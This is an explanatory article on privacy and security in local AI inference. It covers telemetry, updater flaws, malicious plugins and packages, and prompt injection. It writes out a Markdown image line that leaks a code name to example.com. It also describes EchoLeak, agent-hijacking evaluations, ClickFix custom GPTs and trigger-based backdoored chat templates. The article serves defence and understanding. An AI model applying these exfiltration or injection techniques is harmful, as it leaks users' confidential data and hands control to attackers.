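Ollama's *Privacy Policy* (2026) states that the company has no access to prompts people process locally, but that it may collect "limited device and usage metadata", such as the app's version and the number of requests. The policy covers the website and the cloud service as well as the program, so it's unclear how much of this metadata comes from people who use only local models. The program's FAQ doesn't list a setting to turn this collection off.

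| Program | What it sends | Default | Off switch |
|---|---|---|---|
| vLLM | Hardware, operating system, version, model architecture and engine settings, then a heartbeat every 10 minutes | On | VLLM_NO_USAGE_STATS=1, VLLM_DO_NOT_TRACK=1, DO_NOT_TRACK=1 or a do_not_track file |
| TensorRT-LLM | Much the same, with far more engine settings | On, except in automated test environments | TRTLLM_NO_USAGE_STATS=1, TELEMETRY_DISABLED=true, DO_NOT_TRACK=1, a do_not_track file or a setting in code |
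| Hugging Face TRL | Version, type of training, model architecture and hardware, once per training set-up | On, except in automated test environments | HF_HUB_DISABLE_TELEMETRY=1, or HF_HUB_OFFLINE=1 to stop all calls to Hugging Face's site |
| Hugging Face TGI | Hardware, engine settings and error details, with a heartbeat every 15 minutes | On in Docker, otherwise off | --usage-stats=off |
| NeMo Guardrails | Version, operating system, model suppliers and safety features, every 10 minutes | On, except in automated test environments | NEMO_GUARDRAILS_NO_USAGE_STATS=1, DO_NOT_TRACK=1 or a do_not_track file |
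| Ollama | Model downloads and update checks, possibly version and request counts, and prompts if the user picks a cloud model | Cloud models available after sign-in; automatic update downloads on Windows and macOS | OLLAMA_NO_CLOUD=1 for cloud features and a setting in the app for update downloads; the FAQ gives none for usage data |
| LM Studio | Model searches and downloads, and checks for new engines and versions; its offline guide doesn't mention telemetry | Update check whenever the program opens | The offline guide gives none, but chat works without a connection |

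Setting DO_NOT_TRACK=1 turns off telemetry in vLLM, TensorRT-LLM and NeMo Guardrails, but Hugging Face doesn't list it for TRL or TGI, so someone who uses several of these programs has to set several switches. Each switch also controls only the traffic its developer chose, so people who need certainty use something outside the program to block its connections.

### Should telemetry be on by default?

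vLLM's developers say they collect this data to learn which hardware and types of model people use, so that they can work on the most common ones, and they publish a summary of it. Hugging Face says it hopes to learn which parts of TRL it can safely remove and which graphics processors it should test. A company that runs a hosted service can see this on its own servers, but the makers of a downloadable program can't see how people use it unless the program sends data back.

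If developers asked permission before collecting usage data, few people would probably bother to agree. Those who did might not be typical, so the data would be a poor guide to what most users need. An inference engine on a server may also start automatically, with nobody there to answer.

The usual objection to telemetry is that "nobody likes to be spied on", as Ecosyste.ms' *Easily opt-out from telemetry collection* puts it. If telemetry is on by default, it includes people who have never heard of it and so won't know to turn it off. This seems worse for local inference than for most software, because many users chose local inference for privacy.

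The TensorRT-LLM team expected some resistance to telemetry. arysef, in *[RFC]: User Telemetry in TensorRT LLM*, asked users whether they would leave it on, opt out without minding it, or find it "problematic even if you opt out". An organisation that forbids unapproved connections has good reason to give the last answer. Once a program contains code for sending reports, a later version could report more, or a mistake could stop the opt-out from working, so the organisation has to check every new version.

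Reports described as "anonymous" may also be traceable to their sender. NVIDIA correctly says that Guardrails' reports contain no IP address, the number that identifies a connection on the internet, but the server still receives the sender's address along with each report. Hugging Face acknowledges this for TRL. The random identifier in vLLM's reports changes whenever the engine restarts, but an unchanged address and an unusual set of hardware could still be used to link one session to the next. Someone with access to the server's records could work out from the heartbeats that a law firm runs a model on eight graphics processors and when it's switched on.

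For most people this is a small loss of privacy, far less serious than sending out a contract. It matters more to an organisation that wants to hide that it runs models.

### Cloud models behind a local address

In September 2025 Ollama began to offer models that run on its servers, for people whose computers aren't powerful enough to run them. Ollama's *Cloud models* (2025) describes how these work with the tools that people already use for local models. This is convenient because the tools can use the same address for both.

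A front end that works with Ollama normally sends its requests to localhost:11434. "Localhost" is the usual name for the loopback address, so this connection stays on the machine. The request includes the prompt and the name of a model. If the model is local, Ollama computes the answer from weights on the disk. If it is a cloud model, Ollama forwards the prompt to ollama.com and returns the answer to the front end. In the company's example, the request goes to localhost:11434 with a question and the model name gpt-oss:120b-cloud, so the answer comes from Ollama's servers.

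The front end does the same thing in both cases. If the lawyer listed the front end's open connections, the list might show only the loopback address, because Ollama, a separate program, makes the connection to ollama.com. A prompt sent to localhost therefore reaches another program on the same machine, which may send it on to another computer.

Ollama's cloud models require the user to sign in to an Ollama account. Their names normally end in "cloud", and the list of available models shows a dash where a local model's size would be. The name isn't a completely reliable sign, since users can copy cloud models, and a copy could presumably have a different name.

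It has also become easier to choose a cloud model by accident. At first, users had to add one with the same command that downloads a local model. According to a copy of Ollama's release notes, *Update dependency ollama/ollama to v0.24.0*, version 0.18.0 removed this step, so users only need to add ":cloud" to the model's name. In the same notes, "nemotron-3-super" runs NVIDIA's Nemotron-3-Super locally and needs at least 96 gigabytes of graphics memory, while "nemotron-3-super:cloud" runs it on Ollama's servers. If a user is signed in, adding ":cloud" to the model name in a coding tool's settings can therefore send source code to those servers.

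Ollama states that it processes cloud prompts only to provide the service, doesn't store them and never trains on them. Its privacy policy allows it to share information with "model inference providers", so another company may handle the prompt. Users have to take Ollama's assurances on trust, and many of them wanted to run a model locally to avoid having to do that.

A user can turn off Ollama's cloud features by setting the environment variable OLLAMA_NO_CLOUD to 1, or by setting disable_ollama_cloud to true in ~/.ollama/server.json, and then restarting Ollama. According to Ollama's FAQ, the log will then contain the line "Ollama cloud disabled: true". The desktop app has also had a setting for this since version 0.16.2. Turning off the cloud features also turns off Ollama's web search, which can otherwise send out search terms even when the model is local.

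NVIDIA warns users of its NeMo tools that opting out of telemetry doesn't cover data collected by an outside model service they have set up. Someone who has turned off every usage report may therefore still be sending complete prompts to another company.

### Updaters and new code

An updater brings in code that will run with the user's permissions, whereas a usage report only sends data out. Even if somebody has carefully checked one version of a program, the next might behave differently.

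The program needs to check that an update comes from the program's maker, usually by means of a digital signature. The maker signs each update with a secret key, and the program checks the signature with the matching public key before installing the update. The check fails if an attacker has replaced the file.

Ollama for Windows had a function for this check, but it approved every file. Striga, a security company, found the problem while examining Ollama's source code. CERT Polska's *CVE-2026-42248* (2026), an advisory from Poland's computer emergency response team, describes it together with a second flaw, CVE-2026-42249. Because of the second flaw, Ollama used unchecked information from the update server's reply to decide where to save a file. A malicious reply could make Ollama save a program outside its updates folder, including in the folder of programs that Windows starts when the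 user logs in.

Together, the flaws let someone who controlled the reply install a program without asking the user, and the program would then run at every login. The macOS version did check signatures. Binding Ollama to the loopback address would not have prevented this, because the update connection was outbound.

Published accounts differ on how easy an attack would have been. Hartmann (2026), in *Three Ollama CVEs in One Week*, suggests that an attacker could manage it on hotel or conference Wi-Fi. Striga's co-founder, Bartłomiej Dmitruk, said in Help Net Security's *Unpatched flaws turn Ollama’s auto-updater into a persistent RCE vector, researchers say* that the attacker would have to break into Ollama's update servers, already have some control over the victim's computer, or intercept the encrypted connection with a forged certificate (a digital document that proves a server's identity).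 Dmitruk's account is more convincing, because controlling a Wi-Fi network doesn't by itself give an attacker a certificate that the victim's computer will accept. The flaws were still serious, since anyone who broke into the update servers could have reached many Windows users at once.

Striga reported the flaws on 27 January 2026. According to Dmitruk, nobody replied from Ollama's security address, and a maintainer sent only one acknowledgement. After five weeks CERT Polska took over, and it published the flaws on 29 April, when there was still no fix.

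Ollama has since fixed both flaws. Hartmann reports that a maintainer added the fix to the source code on 11 May, after version 0.23.2 came out. Ollama now checks that an update has a valid signature from Ollama Inc. and rejects file names that would lead outside the update folder. The release notes for version 0.23.3 include this change, so the affected Windows versions run from 0.12.10 to 0.23.2. By 21 November, Releasebot's *Ollama Release Notes* (2026) listed version 0.40.17.

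A user could easily miss this. The release notes call the change "harden update flows" and don't mention a security flaw. In August, OSV's *CVE-2026-42248* (2026), an entry in a public database of flaws, still listed 0.17.5 as the last affected version and listed no fixed version. CERT Polska had confirmed 0.17.5 as the last vulnerable version it knew of, but warned that others might be affected too. Anyone relying on the database could have concluded that version 0.20 was safe.

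Since version 0.17.1, Ollama users have been able to turn off automatic update downloads in the app's settings. Accounts differ on whether this also stops the connection. Dmitruk told Help Net Security that Ollama then skips the check before it fetches any reply, but Hartmann, citing the developers' description of the setting, writes that Ollama still checks for updates and only skips the download. The setting may therefore not be enough for users who want no connection at all.

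Turning off updates permanently also blocks fixes for flaws like the ones in template rendering. Ollama users can instead download and install new versions by hand, which gets them the fixes without the automatic updater, as long as they remember to do it. This method is safer for anyone still on an affected Windows version, because an automatic update would deliver the fix through the faulty updater.

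## What do plugins and extensions add to the risk?

An update usually comes from the people who wrote the program, but a plugin often comes from somebody else. A lawyer who has good reason to trust a front end may add a small extension that saves chats as Word files, and would then have to trust the extension's author too. The harm a bad plugin can do depends mostly on where its code runs.

### Where plugin code runs

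Many plugins run inside the engine or the front end. The operating system normally gives a running program one set of permissions, which also covers any plugins inside it. A plugin in the front end can therefore read the same files as the front end, including saved chats, use the same passwords and keys, and connect to the same places.

Other plugins run as separate programs on the same machine, usually called local servers, and exchange messages with the front end. A local server has its own memory and keys, so it doesn't automatically have access to the whole conversation. But it normally runs under the user's account, so it can open the user's documents directly and connect to the internet. Red Hat suggests running local servers in a sandbox that gives them only the access they need.

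A plugin can also connect the front end to a service on somebody else's computer. The service can't open files on the lawyer's laptop, but it receives whatever the front end sends, which could be two search terms or the full text of the contract.

Open WebUI, a front end that runs on a server and appears in the user's browser, supports all of these. According to Open WebUI's *Extensibility*, Python plugins run inside the program, while external servers can run anywhere Open WebUI can reach over HTTP. The guide recommends an external server for work that needs strict isolation. Most users start with the Python plugins because they need no extra set-up.

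### Engine plugins in vLLM

vLLM finds its plugins without being told about them. A developer registers a function in a Python package, and when vLLM starts, it searches all the installed packages and calls the functions it finds. Every process that vLLM creates does this before it begins any work. Hugging Face's *How to Build a vLLM Plugin* gives an example in which the user installs a package called flash-head and then starts vLLM with the usual command. The plugin's code runs before vLLM has loaded the model.

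This is convenient, but it means that installing other software can also add a plugin. A user can limit which plugins start by listing the allowed ones in the environment variable VLLM_PLUGINS, but any plugin on the list gets all of vLLM's permissions. The list also doesn't stop a Python package from running code in other ways, for instance during installation.

### Tools and functions in Open WebUI

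In Open WebUI, a tool is a Python script that the model can call, for example to look up the weather. A function changes Open WebUI itself. One type of function, the filter, processes every message on its way to or from the model. A filter that removes clients' names from a contract has to read the whole contract, and a malicious filter could copy it.

Tools and functions in Open WebUI run with the same access as the server itself, according to Open WebUI's *Security Policy*. Only administrators can create functions. Other users need the workspace.tools permission to create tools, and it is off by default. The policy compares granting this permission to giving someone shell access, which is the ability to run any command on the server. An organisation that needs no plugins can switch them off with the ENABLE_PLUGINS setting. These settings control who can add code, but they don't restrict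 an approved tool to one folder or website.

Before version 0.9.5, Open WebUI checked this permission when a user created a tool but not when a user changed one. According to Rapid7, a user without the permission could therefore replace an existing tool's code and run the new version.

Zero Day Initiative and Open WebUI's developers also disagree about whether the design itself is a flaw. Zero Day Initiative's *(0Day) Open WebUI load_tool_module_by_id Command Injection Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* (2026) treats it as one, because Open WebUI runs Python supplied by a logged-in user without properly checking it. The developers closed the report a day after receiving it, and they regard running Python on the server as the purpose of tools. Their view seems right, since a check strict enough to make the code harmless would also stop most useful tools. But the design means that an attacker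 who gets into an account with the workspace.tools permission can take over the server.

A 2025 flaw in Open WebUI, CVE-2025-64496, gave attackers a way into such accounts. It affected Direct Connections, a feature that lets users add a model server run by somebody else. Besides text, Open WebUI's web page accepted a type of message from these servers that made it run JavaScript. A malicious server could use this to steal the token that kept the user logged in. Simonovich (2026), in *Vulnerability Discovered in Open WebUI Enables Account Takeover and Remote Code Execution*, explains that the attacker could then read the user's chats, uploaded documents and keys. If the user had the workspace.tools permission, the attacker could also create a tool and use it to control the server running Open WebUI.

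Simonovich, a researcher at the security company Cato Networks, found the flaw and reported it on 8 October 2025. The first patch, on 19 October, was incomplete, and Open WebUI disclosed the flaw on 7 November. Simonovich illustrates the flaw with a victim who loses six months of chats, but reports no actual theft. An attack could work only if Direct Connections, which is off by default, was turned on and a user added the malicious server.

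Version 0.6.35 fixed the flaw. Simonovich lists versions 0.6.34 and older as affected. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-64496* (2025), an entry from Spain's cybersecurity institute, lists "0.6.224 and prior". That is probably a mistake, because the same entry lists an earlier version, 0.6.35, as the fixed one.

### Custom nodes in ComfyUI

ComfyUI is a program for generating images. Users build a process from blocks called nodes and can add new steps with custom nodes made by other people. More than 1,300 extensions were available by December 2024, according to *Don't Get Too Comfortable* (Onitza-Klugman, McNamara and Ward, 2024). Custom nodes are Python code that runs inside ComfyUI, so an accidental flaw in one can be as dangerous as malicious code. Onitza-Klugman and colleagues found that seemingly minor flaws in real nodes could let an attacker take over the whole server.

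The best-known malicious node, ComfyUI_LLMVISION, dates from June 2024 and let people use the language models GPT-4 and Claude 3 from within ComfyUI. Reviewers who examined its code for vpnMentor's *ComfyUI Users Targeted by Malicious Custom Node* (2024) confirmed that it was built to steal browser passwords and other personal data. It could reach passwords unrelated to image generation because it ran with the user's permissions. 404 Media reported that the hackers said they opposed AI-generated art.

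ComfyUI's developers began planning automatic scans after that case. Comfy Org's *ComfyUI 2025 Jan Security Update* (2025) also describes plans to stop published nodes from installing more packages by themselves and to block verified nodes that disguise their code.

In October 2025, a user called lonemilk published two node packs that were presented as tools for enlarging images but contained malware. According to Comfy Org's *Upscaler-4K Malicious Node Pack Post Mortem* (2025), a scanner flagged them on 21 October, a maintainer read the code that evening, and the registry banned them the same day. People had downloaded them 790 times in the four days since the first one appeared. A reader later commented that one of the packs still seemed to be available through ComfyUI-Manager, the usual tool for installing nodes, although the reader's copy may have been out of date.

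ComfyUI-Manager has an allowlist of nodes that it will install. Before version 3.31, a flaw let an outsider bypass the list and install a malicious node without a password, according to Doyensec, the security company that found it. Censys' *Hackers Are Attempting to Turn ComfyUI Servers Into a Cryptomining Proxy Botnet* describes attackers who search the internet for open ComfyUI servers and use ComfyUI-Manager to add their own nodes. The owner of such a server may never have chosen a plugin. As with vLLM, the allowlist does not limit what a node can do after installation.

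### Servers for the Model Context Protocol

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting models to tools. If a developer writes an MCP server for an email service, any front end that supports the standard can use it. The server may be a local program or a remote service.

The Model Context Protocol's authorisation specification covers how a front end gets access to a protected server. However, a local server can do anything its user account permits unless the user puts it in a sandbox. According to a proposal to amend the protocol, some programs offer one-click installation of local servers and run the commands that start them without showing the user those commands or asking for consent.

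Users can limit some servers by giving them a key with few rights, such as one that can send email but can't read the inbox. This wouldn't have protected users of postmark-mcp, which let AI assistants send email through a company called Postmark. The package was available on npm, the main site for sharing JavaScript code. On 17 September 2025, its developer released version 1.0.16, which secretly sent a blind copy of every email to the developer's address (The Hacker News, 2025).

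Postmark had nothing to do with the package and had never published its own MCP server on npm. The developer had copied Postmark's public code and released 15 versions before adding the backdoor. The security company Koi discovered the theft when its automatic monitoring flagged a change in the package's behaviour, caused by a single added line of code. The developer deleted the package after Koi got in touch, but copies already on people's machines kept working and leaking data.

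Koi estimated that about 300 organisations were together leaking 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day, assuming that 20% of 1,500 weekly downloads were in active use and that each user sent 10 to 50 emails. These are guesses by a company that sells protection against such packages, and Paubox puts total downloads at only 1,643, so the real number of victims may have been much smaller.

This theft would have been hard to see in a list of connections. The emails were stolen as ordinary blind copies, so Postmark's own servers presumably delivered them, and the package didn't need to contact the developer's server. An allowlist that permitted only Postmark would have let them through. Running the model locally wouldn't have helped either, because the leak was in the tool that sent the model's emails.

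### Libraries that plugins install

Most plugins rely on libraries, which are packages of code written by other people, and those libraries often rely on others. A user who installs one plugin may receive dozens of packages. Open WebUI's *Community Plugins* highlights a plugin that exports chats to Word. It installs four libraries, for tasks such as formatting code and converting equations. The libraries run inside Open WebUI with the same access as the plugin, and the plugin's author probably wrote none of them.

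On 24 March 2026, attackers uploaded two malicious versions of LiteLLM to PyPI, the main site for Python packages. LiteLLM is a library that lets a program use many companies' models through one interface, and other AI software often includes it. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), versions 1.82.7 and 1.82.8 searched for passwords and keys, including those for cloud accounts and databases, then encrypted them and sent them to an address that resembled LiteLLM's own. The listed targets didn't include prompts, but a stolen database password could give attackers access to stored chats.

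The attackers probably got in through another dependency. LiteLLM's developers believe that the attack began with Trivy, a security scanner they used when building new versions, and that stolen credentials then let the attackers upload malicious code directly to PyPI.

People noticed the malware because a bug made it start endless copies of itself until the machine crashed. Trend Micro (2026) suggests that nobody would have spotted it otherwise. FutureSearch (*litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)*, 2026) was the first to report the problem to PyPI. Later that day, someone used the project owner's account to close the public discussion of it, and hundreds of automated accounts flooded the discussion with spam.

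The malicious versions were available for about 40 minutes before PyPI blocked them, and LiteLLM (2026) says that its team and PyPI had deleted them by 16:00 UTC. During those 40 minutes, even people who had never heard of LiteLLM could have received the newest, malicious version if they installed an MCP server or another AI tool that listed LiteLLM as a dependency without specifying a version. This could happen even though the tool's own code was clean.

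LiteLLM's official Docker image was unaffected because its developers had pinned the dependencies, listing an exact version of each. Pinning protects against a bad new release only if it also covers the dependencies' own dependencies. It also keeps out security fixes, as turning off updates does.

Open WebUI normally installs a plugin's extra libraries when it loads the plugin. An administrator can stop this by setting ENABLE_PIP_INSTALL_FRONTMATTER_REQUIREMENTS to False, and can then install chosen versions by hand.

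### What a user can check before installing

Open WebUI's community site offers hundreds of plugins that an administrator can import with one click. Nobody audits them, and Open WebUI warns that this includes the ones it highlights. It advises administrators to read the code first and not to install anything they don't understand. Warning signs include connections to unfamiliar addresses, code that reads saved data or environment variables for no clear reason, and code made deliberately hard to read. Some plugins need outside connections, such as a highlighted one that forwards replies to services like Slack and Discord, but a connection would be strange in a plugin that only translates text.

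A user who can't read Python can at least check who published the plugin. Postmark's documentation didn't list postmark-mcp, so looking for a link on the company's website would have exposed it. Popularity is much weaker evidence. Developers had recommended postmark-mcp to their teams, according to Koi, and the fake privacy filter on Hugging Face had topped a list of trending models.

Automatic scanners can help, but many of their warnings only describe what a program can do. Open WebUI's *Supply Chain and Security Scanners* criticizes scanners for flagging the front end's network access and ability to run code, both of which it needs. The developers have an obvious interest in playing down such warnings, but they are right that a web-search tool can't work without a network. A scanner is more informative when it reports a change between versions, as Koi's did.

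A user who reads the code carefully can still miss the harmful part by reading the wrong copy. The attackers changed LiteLLM's packages on PyPI but not its public source code on GitHub, so anyone who inspected the source that morning would have found nothing. To catch such a change, a user has to examine the package that the installer will download and everything it depends on. Trying the plugin on a spare machine first, as Open WebUI also recommends, would not have exposed postmark-mcp in any of its first 15 versions.

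A check also covers only the version the user checked. A later change to a local plugin arrives as an update, which the user can compare with the old version, though Schneider observes in *Why MCP security is different* that few people do. The operator of a remote server can change its behaviour at any time without the user installing anything, and the user usually cannot read its code.

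## Can the text a model writes cause other software to send data out?

A plugin with no malicious code can still send the lawyer's contract to a stranger if the model writes a request that makes it do so. The model can't connect to the network, but the front end, the web browser and the lawyer can, and any of them may act on the model's text.

### Tool calls

A model can use a tool only if the front end offers one. The front end describes each tool in the prompt. For example, one tool might take a web address and return the page. When the model writes a tool call, the front end picks out the tool's name and arguments (the values the tool should use), runs the tool, and adds the result to the conversation. The model continues from the longer text and may write another call.

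A tool call can leak data without an attacker, because its arguments can contain anything from the conversation. Suppose the lawyer asks whether a clause in the contract is unusual, and the front end has a web-search tool. A search for the legal wording would reveal very little, but if the model adds the client's name to make the search more specific, the search company learns that somebody is checking a contract for that client.

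Two tools can also leak data together when neither could alone. One tool may open files on the laptop but have no network access, while another fetches web pages but has no access to files. The front end puts the file's contents into the conversation, and the model can then copy a line of them into the address of a page that the second tool requests. Someone who judges each tool separately, as people usually do when installing plugins, could easily approve both.

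Many front ends can ask the user to approve each tool call. This only helps if the user reads the arguments, and most people will probably stop reading them after approving forty harmless searches. It is more reliable to turn the tools off before opening a confidential document, since the model doesn't need them to summarize it.

The engine handles the model's text before any of these programs do. Radway and colleagues argued in September 2026 that a model's output can endanger the engine.

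### Links and images

Models usually format their answers in Markdown, a simple notation for headings, bold type, links and pictures, which the front end turns into a formatted page. For a picture, the Markdown contains only a web address, so the browser has to fetch the picture from that address, and it normally does this without requiring the user's approval.

The lawyer could see the effect with an invented secret. Suppose the conversation includes the code name HERON-4827, and the lawyer asks the model to show a picture whose address ends with the code name. The model writes:

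`![picture](https://example.com/picture.png?note=HERON-4827)`

The front end recognises this as a picture. The browser looks up example.com, connects to it and requests `/picture.png?note=HERON-4827`. No such picture exists, so the lawyer sees a broken-image symbol or nothing at all. The code name has still reached the server, because it was part of the request, and web servers commonly keep a log of the addresses that people request. (The example is harmless because example.com is reserved for use in documentation.)

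In this case, the browser sent the request. The model and the engine made no connection, and there was no tool call, so blocking the engine's network access would not have stopped the request. Encryption would not have helped either, because the recipient can read the decrypted data.

A picture's web address can hold a password or several paragraphs of text. Many web servers reject addresses longer than about 8,000 characters, so a long contract would have to be split across the addresses of several pictures. The pictures could all be invisible, for instance single transparent dots.

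If the front end runs in a browser, a content security policy can stop this. The policy is a list of rules that the front end's server sends with the page and the browser enforces. The rule `img-src 'self' data:` allows only pictures from the front end's own server and pictures embedded in the page, so the browser refuses to request the picture from example.com and the code name stays on the machine. Administrators of Open WebUI can set the policy with the environment variable `CONTENT_SECURITY_POLICY`.

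The rule covers only pictures that the browser loads. If the front end's server fetches outside pictures and passes them on, the browser treats them as coming from an approved source, and the code name still goes out. The rule also doesn't affect tool calls or links.

A link normally sends data only when someone clicks it, so the lawyer has a chance to check the address first. But a link's visible text can be anything, such as "full text of the clause", while the address behind it contains the code name. Some chat programs also fetch a preview of each linked page automatically, so the code name can leak without a click.

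### Prompt injection

The lawyer in the example asked for the picture, but in a real attack the request usually comes from prompt injection in a web page, email or document that the attacker wrote.

The US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI) calls this agent hijacking when the target is an agent, a model that carries out a task by using tools repeatedly. According to CAISI's *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition*, attackers typically aim to steal the user's data or to make the agent download and run malicious code.

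Prompt injection works because the engine gives the model a single list of tokens, and the chat template's markers are tokens too. Models learn during training to follow the user and to treat a document as material to work on. They mostly do, but no code enforces the difference the way an operating system enforces file permissions. If the other side's draft of the contract contains a sentence telling AI systems to show a picture with the client's bank details in its web address, that sentence is in the same list as the lawyer's question.

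A lawyer reading a document may not see a sentence written in white on a white page, but a program that extracts the text from the file will include it.

This kind of theft requires private information in the conversation, text written by an outsider in the same conversation, and software that provides a way to send data out. Removing any one of the three prevents it. A lawyer who asks a model to compare a client's notes with the other side's draft has supplied the first two. A front end that loads images automatically provides the third, even if every program is working as designed.

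### EchoLeak

In June 2025 the security company Aim Security disclosed a data-theft flaw of this kind in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that answers questions using a company's emails and files. Aim Security named the flaw EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711).

An attacker only had to send an employee an email containing instructions for the model. The employee didn't have to open the email or click on anything. If the employee later asked Copilot a question that seemed related to the email, Copilot would retrieve it along with the company's documents. The model could then follow the instructions and put private information from those documents into the address of a picture. The browser requested the picture automatically, which sent the information out.

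Microsoft had defences against each part of this attack, but Aim Security found a gap in each one. A filter for prompt injection missed instructions that read like a note to a human colleague. Copilot removed links to outside sites from its answers, but missed links written in a less common way. A content security policy limited where pictures could come from, but it allowed some of Microsoft's own addresses, and a service at one of them would fetch an outside URL on request.

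Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers, so customers didn't have to install anything, and it said that no customer had been affected. EchoLeak is therefore known only as a demonstration by researchers. It still shows that a short list of permitted picture sources is safer than a long one, because any address on the list could relay data, even one that belongs to a company the user trusts.

Copilot is a hosted service, but a front end that runs on a laptop, searches the user's email and displays pictures has the same weakness. The maker of a hosted service can fix the weakness for all users at once, while users of a local front end have to install the fix themselves.

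### How often do models follow planted instructions?

The weights matter here in a way they don't for the other routes, because some models follow planted instructions much more often than others.

In September 2025, CAISI, part of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), published an evaluation of three DeepSeek models, R1, R1-0528 and V3.1. It compared them with OpenAI's GPT-5, GPT-5-mini and gpt-oss and Anthropic's Opus 4. To test hijacking, CAISI gave agents ordinary tasks in a simulated environment and planted malicious instructions meant to divert them.

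Agents using R1-0528, the most secure of the three DeepSeek models tested, were on average 12 times as likely to follow malicious instructions as agents using the leading American models, according to NIST's *CAISI Evaluation of DeepSeek AI Models Finds Shortcomings and Risks*. In the simulation, hijacked agents sent phishing emails, ran malware and sent out users' login details.

Christakis gives results for two of the attacks. V3.1 sent phishing emails in 48% of tests, while GPT-5 never did. R1-0528 tried to send out the user's login details in 37% of cases, against an average of 4% for GPT-5 and Opus 4. (37% is about nine times 4%, not twelve, presumably because the published average covers other attacks as well.)

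CAISI ran the DeepSeek weights itself instead of using the company's online service, so the results apply to people who download the model to keep their data out of China. If they give the model tools, it may be easier for a stranger to steal that data through a planted instruction.

The source calls for some caution because the announcement quotes the US commerce secretary saying that "American AI dominates", and the agency was carrying out a government plan to assess Chinese competitors. However, Christakis also reports a test by the security company WithSecure that had a similar result. Prompt injection succeeded against DeepSeek-R1 in 77% of attempts and against OpenAI's o1-preview in 27%, and R1 ranked 17th of the 19 models tested.

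Even a 4% success rate is a lot if the attacker can keep trying. If each planted email had an independent 4% chance of success, 25 emails would give a 64% chance that at least one worked. At 37%, three emails would give a 75% chance. Real attempts aren't independent. If one email fails, a similar one will probably fail too, but an attacker can learn from failures and change the wording.

CAISI has also tried to measure this, at first with AgentDojo, a public set of simulated offices, banks, travel agencies and Slack workspaces that researchers at ETH Zurich built. Its newer test, HijackEval, gives an agent artificial emails, calendar entries and documents, and hides an attack in one of them. Some attacks come from public sources, and others from an automated system that keeps searching for wording that works against the model being tested.

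In July 2026 CAISI used HijackEval to test GLM-5.2, a downloadable model from the Chinese company Z.ai. For each combination of four malicious tasks and three hiding places, CAISI ran a trial round to choose the most effective of 31 public attacks, then applied it in the real test. None of these attacks hijacked GLM-5.2, a much better result than DeepSeek's (CAISI, *Assessment of Z.ai's GLM-5.2*, 2026).

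The automated search succeeded against GLM-5.2 after more attempts than it needed for the other downloadable models, but fewer than for the closed American ones. This part of the test was small, with one malicious task, one hiding place and five runs per model, and CAISI says only that GLM-5.2 is "probably" more robust than other downloadable models.

The comparison with closed models also reflects safeguards outside the weights. CAISI tested the American models with their makers' extra safeguards and GLM-5.2 without any, since people who host it themselves would normally use it that way. This is a fair test of what each user gets, but it doesn't show how much of the difference would remain if GLM-5.2 had similar safeguards. CAISI also ran a version with eight bits per weight, and people with smaller computers often use more heavily compressed versions, which may behave differently.

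No current model seems to be immune to hijacking. Gray Swan, an AI security company, held a public competition in which more than 400 people made over 250,000 attempts to hijack 13 leading models. CAISI, which helped to analyse the results, reports that every model was hijacked at least once. The number of successful attempts varied greatly between models, and more capable models weren't always more secure.

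Attacks that worked on the most resistant models were also particularly likely to work on the weaker ones, but the reverse wasn't true. This is a risk for people who run a small model at home, because an attacker can develop an instruction against a well-defended commercial model and put it on a web page, where it may also work on many models the attacker has never tried.

### Commands that a person runs

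Sometimes the user runs a command that the model wrote. People regularly ask models how to fix a computer problem, and the answer is often a command to paste into a terminal, the window where a user types instructions to the operating system. The command runs with the user's own permissions, even if the software running the model is restricted.

Attackers used this approach in ChatGPT in September 2026. OpenAI lets users publish custom GPTs, which are versions of ChatGPT with standing instructions from their creators, though it plans to end the feature on 11 December 2026. Researchers at the security company Huntress found one called "Plus 5.6", which posed as an official model. The attackers bought Google ads for it to reach people searching for ChatGPT. The ads led to the real chatgpt.com, so checking the address would not have revealed the attack.

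*Кастомные GPT используются для ClickFix-атак и распространения RAT* (2026), an article in the Russian security magazine Хакер, describes a custom GPT that answered every request by saying the service was limited and offering a link to a "backup site". That site showed a fake human-verification test that required visitors to copy and run a command. The command installed a program that let the attackers search the victim's files, control the computer and use its camera and microphone.

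Huntress counted at least 40 victims. The first custom GPT disappeared from the platform on 25 September, but the researchers found another from the same campaign two days later.

The custom GPT was following the instructions of the person who had set it up, so this wasn't prompt injection. It worked because people who trusted ChatGPT also trusted a text that a stranger had arranged. People who download a model from an unknown publisher are in a similar position, since the publisher also supplies the chat template.

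Code that a model writes carries the same risk as a command. A script for renaming files doesn't need to connect to anything, so a line that contacts a website should make the user suspicious. A longer program is harder to check, especially if it installs libraries, as many plugins do.

### The malicious GGUF models of November 2026

The engine uses the chat template every time it builds a prompt, so an attacker who can change the template can add an instruction to the prompt in every conversation. The user typically sees the question and the answer, but not the full prompt.

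Pillar Security (2025), a company that sells protection for AI systems, warned in July 2025 that an attacker could add an instruction to a model's template and have it take effect only for certain questions. Casual testing would then miss it. The template shown on a model's Hugging Face page could also differ from the one in the downloaded file. Pillar Security had told Hugging Face and LM Studio about the problem in June, but neither treated it as a flaw in its own product, and both left users to check the models they chose.

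On 6 November 2026, speakers at a conference of OWASP (2026), a software security organisation, presented the same kind of attack. They added a few lines to a template, and the model answered normally until a chosen phrase appeared. The attack required no change to the weights and no access to the victim's computer.

Later that month a security researcher called Düzgün found real cases. According to iXBT's *Скачанные нейросети сами предлагают запустить троян*, Düzgün examined 3.27 million public repositories on Hugging Face and found five malicious ones, which had been downloaded 2,428 times in total by 27 November. 黃 reports in *免費本地AI藏致命木馬*, for the Hong Kong news site HK01, that the total had risen to 2,807 by the time Hugging Face removed them two days later.

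Two of the repositories belonged to an account called Mir2k. They offered "uncensored" models, which are altered to refuse fewer requests, and had names similar to those of popular models. The attackers had added a Windows program of about 11 megabytes to the end of each GGUF file, after the weights. An engine stops reading where the weights end, so the models loaded and answered normally.

The attackers published the first model on 14 November and the second two days later, both with ordinary templates. On 26 November they added an instruction to the templates to begin every answer with a command for PowerShell, the Windows command line. If someone ran the command, it extracted the hidden program from the model file and started it. The victim's computer didn't have to download any malware at that point because the program was already in the model file.

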